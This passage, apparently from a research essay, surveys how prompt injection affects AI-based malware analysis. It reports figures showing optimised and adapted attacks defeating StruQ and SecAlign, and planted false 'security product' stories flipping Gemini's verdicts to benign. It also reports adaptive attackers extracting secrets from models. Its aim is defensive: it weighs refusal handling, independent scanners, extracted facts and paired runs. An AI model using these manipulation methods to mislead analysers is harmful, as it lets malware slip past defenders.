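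Jia and colleagues used a wider range of tasks. Scores in the table run from 0 to 1. A high score on ordinary tasks is good, while a high score under attack means the model performed the attacker's task.

| Model | Ordinary tasks | Handwritten attack | Optimised attack | Optimised attack adapted to the defence |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No added defence | 0.65 | 0.52 | 1.00 | 1.00 |
| StruQ | 0.54 | 0.03 | 0.80 | 1.00 |
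| SecAlign | 0.48 | 0.06 | 0.24 | 0.46 |

StruQ and SecAlign nearly eliminated the handwritten attack, but an automated search for effective wording defeated StruQ most of the time. The adapted attack, which also imitated the defences' markers, always defeated StruQ and almost doubled the score against SecAlign. On a second set of tasks, the adapted attack scored 0.88 against SecAlign. The results for the optimised attacks come from only 50 cases on the first set of tasks and 25 on the second, but the differences are large. Training also made the models worse at ordinary tasks, where the score fell by about a quarter with SecAlign.

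Jia and colleagues also tested GPT-4o-mini, which OpenAI had trained to prioritise the operator's instructions over those in other text. The handwritten attack scored 0.68 and 0.75 on the two sets of tasks, close to the model's scores on ordinary work (0.71 and 0.73). These models are now old, so the figures are weak evidence about current ones. Testing against one familiar attack is still not enough, because a model that resists it may fail against another.

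*Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) similarly argues that a model trained on known attacks may not resist new ones, because people can write only a limited variety of examples by hand. Google therefore trained Gemini on a much broader range of attacks and scenarios, aiming to help it resist attacks that weren't in its training data.

### Resistance to orders and resistance to false stories

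The September 2026 *ALIBI* paper compared how direct orders and a plausible cover story affect malware analysis. Researchers at 78ResearchLab in Seoul tested Gemini 2.5 Pro on 50 malicious Windows programs, and it initially labelled 35 of them malicious. Adding direct orders to the programs changed none of those 35 verdicts, but adding a coherent, false description of the program as a legitimate security product changed 30 of them to "benign".

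GPT-5.5 Pro and Claude Opus 4.7 were misled less often, but they often lowered their severity and confidence ratings even when they kept the same label. A lower rating can help an attacker by moving a file down the analysts' queue. In a test with Linux programs, Gemini changed 16 of 40 verdicts to "benign".

The researchers wrote the false story in advance and gave each model one chance to analyse each file, so the story worked without the repeated attempts that an adaptive attacker would make. A defensive prompt that told the model to verify claims roughly halved the number of "benign" verdicts, but Gemini still called 42.9% of the malicious samples benign.

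Training a model to reject injected orders doesn't address this attack. Support Gate's rule is more relevant, since it would treat a company name in a file as text and not as proof of who made the program. A pipeline could have ordinary software check the file's digital signature, which identifies the publisher, and give the result to the model as a verified fact. The attack isn't designed to defeat this check. But many legitimate programs are unsigned, so a missing signature doesn't prove that a program is malicious.

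### Defences against attackers who adapt

*Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (2026) describes an automated attacker that revised its messages over hundreds of rounds. It made more than 20,000 attempts to extract secrets from a model under nine arrangements of defences. Every defence that relied on the model to protect itself eventually failed. The only defence that worked was a conventional program that checked each response before the user received it, and no secrets leaked in 15,000 attacks against it.

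The researchers also tested Gemini 2.5 Pro, GPT-5.4 and Claude Sonnet 4.6 with their default safety settings. All three revealed every secret. Gemini and GPT-5.4 did so within ten rounds, while Claude took longer.

This supports putting important decisions in ordinary software, as Tool Authorization does. But a verdict is harder to protect than a secret. A program can search every response for a known secret, but it has no correct answer to compare with a malware report's verdict of "benign". It can confirm that the report has the correct format or that a cited function exists, but a well-written false report would pass those checks.

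*Beyond Pattern Matching* (2026) summarises two broader studies of adaptive attacks. Zhan and colleagues tested eight defences against indirect injection and bypassed all of them, with success rates above 50%. *The Attacker Moves Second* (2025) reported success rates above 90% against twelve published defences. *Beyond Pattern Matching* attributes such results to attackers who can use the model's internal calculations or find out which inputs a defence blocks. It argues that defences last longer when they depend on something an attacker can't easily change, such as the origin of the text, which Provenance Gate uses, or disagreement between models.

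### Handling refusals

ESET advises organisations to find out what their AI tools do when they refuse or can't finish a task. A refusal lets malware through only if the system treats it as a pass, so the safest rule is to accept only a complete answer in the expected format. If the tool refused, returned garbled text or stopped early, the file would stay unapproved until another check had examined it.

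If a person always does that check, the workload can be heavy. According to Help Net Security, a trained analyst may need hours to weeks to confirm a malware verdict. Suppose a scanner checks 10,000 files a day and the model refuses 1% of them. At two hours per file, the 100 daily refusals would occupy 25 analysts working eight-hour days.

An easier next step would be to rerun the model without the file's comments and strings, since one of them probably triggered the refusal. The pipeline could then run conventional tools and send only the files still unresolved to a person. Removing text only after a refusal would limit the loss of information to those files. There appears to be no published test of this sequence.

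Human reviewers also make mistakes, especially if they start from the model's conclusion. Help Net Security describes a study in which security professionals with generative AI did no better than beginners without it, and struggled to notice the tool's errors. Other research found that people trust automated answers too much even after learning about the risk. A reviewer could examine the conventional tools' results before reading the model's report, although nobody seems to have tested whether this helps with injected text.

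### Independent static and behavioural checks

ESET recommends against giving any language model sole authority to declare code safe. A pipeline can follow this advice by running conventional tools separately and keeping their detections, whatever the model concludes. Such tools still work on Hades, according to the Socket analysis that Schneier quotes.

The effect of injected text depends partly on how the model's result is combined with a conventional scanner's. If the scanner misses 20% of malware, the model misses 30%, and their errors are independent, blocking every file that either one detects gives a combined miss rate of 0.20 × 0.30, or 6%. Injected text that always made the model miss malware would raise this to 20%, the scanner's own miss rate. If the model's result could override the scanner's, the miss rate with the same text would be 100%.

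The mistakes may not be independent. The static engines that missed macOS.Gaslight, for example, wouldn't have corrected a model that accepted its false messages. The changes that the malware study *ALIBI* made to its Windows programs also stopped Microsoft's antivirus from detecting 10 of the 39 samples it had previously caught. The study attributes these missed detections to changes in the files' structure, not to the false story, but they show that a single modification can weaken two defences.

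Behavioural checks, which run the program in a sandbox, depend less on the text in the file. Malware can still avoid them by doing nothing harmful when it detects a virtual machine, as Skynet tried to do. If a defender flags a file whenever any one tool detects it, the tools' false alarms add up, so the defender has to measure those too.

ESET also suggests using several models. This is more likely to help if each model analyses the file separately and the pipeline uses a fixed rule to compare their answers, because agents that pass text to one another can also pass on an attacker's message. In the *ALIBI* study of vulnerability detectors, debate between agents didn't protect VulTrial. Santos-Grueiro cites research by Chang and colleagues on Magentic-One, a system in which several agents share a task. Indirect injection made it run harmful code in 72–80% of attempts, compared with 2–4% for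 a single agent using the same model.

### Facts extracted before the model reads the program

Another possibility is to have conventional software read the strings and give the model only facts in a fixed format. For a program that steals passwords, the model might receive:

```
Reads a file that stores passwords: yes
Sends data over the network: yes
Destination on a list of known malicious addresses: no
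Claims to come from a security company: yes
Valid signature from that company: no
```

The model would receive much more information than placeholders provide, but none of the attacker's wording. As with YARA and capa rules, that information would be limited to what the developers had thought to include.

*MARS* (2026) applies fixed rules at a later stage, to score the claims a language model makes about malware. The two methods could be combined so that software controls both the facts the model receives and the claims that reach the report.

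Santos-Grueiro's larger experiment included structured records, but these still contained the program's text. The planted text had no statistically clear effect with either the records or the ordinary prompt, so the experiment can't show that the structure helped. Apparently no one has published a comparison of a model analysing the same malware with its full text and with extracted facts alone. Jacob and colleagues' shopping agent suggests that the method can prevent injected orders, but not that the facts would be enough for malware analysis.

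### Comparing runs with and without strings

A pipeline could also run the model twice, once on the complete program and once with its strings masked, and block the file if either run labels it malicious. Text injected into the strings could mislead only the first run, and the second might still detect the malware.

A paired system misses a file only if both runs miss it. With the symbols from the break-even condition for stripping (*s* for the miss rate without strings, *m*<sub>0</sub> and *m*<sub>1</sub> for the rates with them, and *q* for the share of malware with injected text), its miss rate is at most

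$$(1-q)\min(m_0, s) + q\min(m_1, s)$$

This assumes that masking removes all of the injected text, and that *s* is the same for both kinds of malware. Suppose *m*<sub>0</sub> is 20%, *m*<sub>1</sub> is 80%, *s* is 30% and *q* is 10%. A model that always reads the strings would miss 26% of malware, and one that never reads them would miss 30%. The paired system would miss at most 21%. Under these assumptions, it cannot miss more malware than either method alone.

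Running the analysis twice, once with strings and once without, takes more compute and adds false alarms. If the run with strings wrongly flagged 2% of harmless programs and the run without them wrongly flagged 5%, a system that flags a program when either run does would wrongly flag between 5% and 7%.

No published study seems to have tested paired runs with and without strings. The closest evidence is Thornton's test of paired runs with and without comments, and the two-stage defence in *ALIBI*, a study of vulnerability detection. That defence had mixed results, which is a reason to keep both runs' findings under a fixed rule, so that neither set can override the other.

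If the model is an agent, each run also needs its own conversation and saved notes. Otherwise, during the run without strings, the agent might read a summary from the other run that repeats the attacker's claim.

A pipeline could use disagreement between the runs as a warning, but not as proof of an attack. Reassuring injected text would tend to produce a "benign" verdict with strings and a "malicious" one without them. A legitimate backup program could produce the same result, because without its help text and company name it may look like a program that just copies a user's files and sends them to a server.
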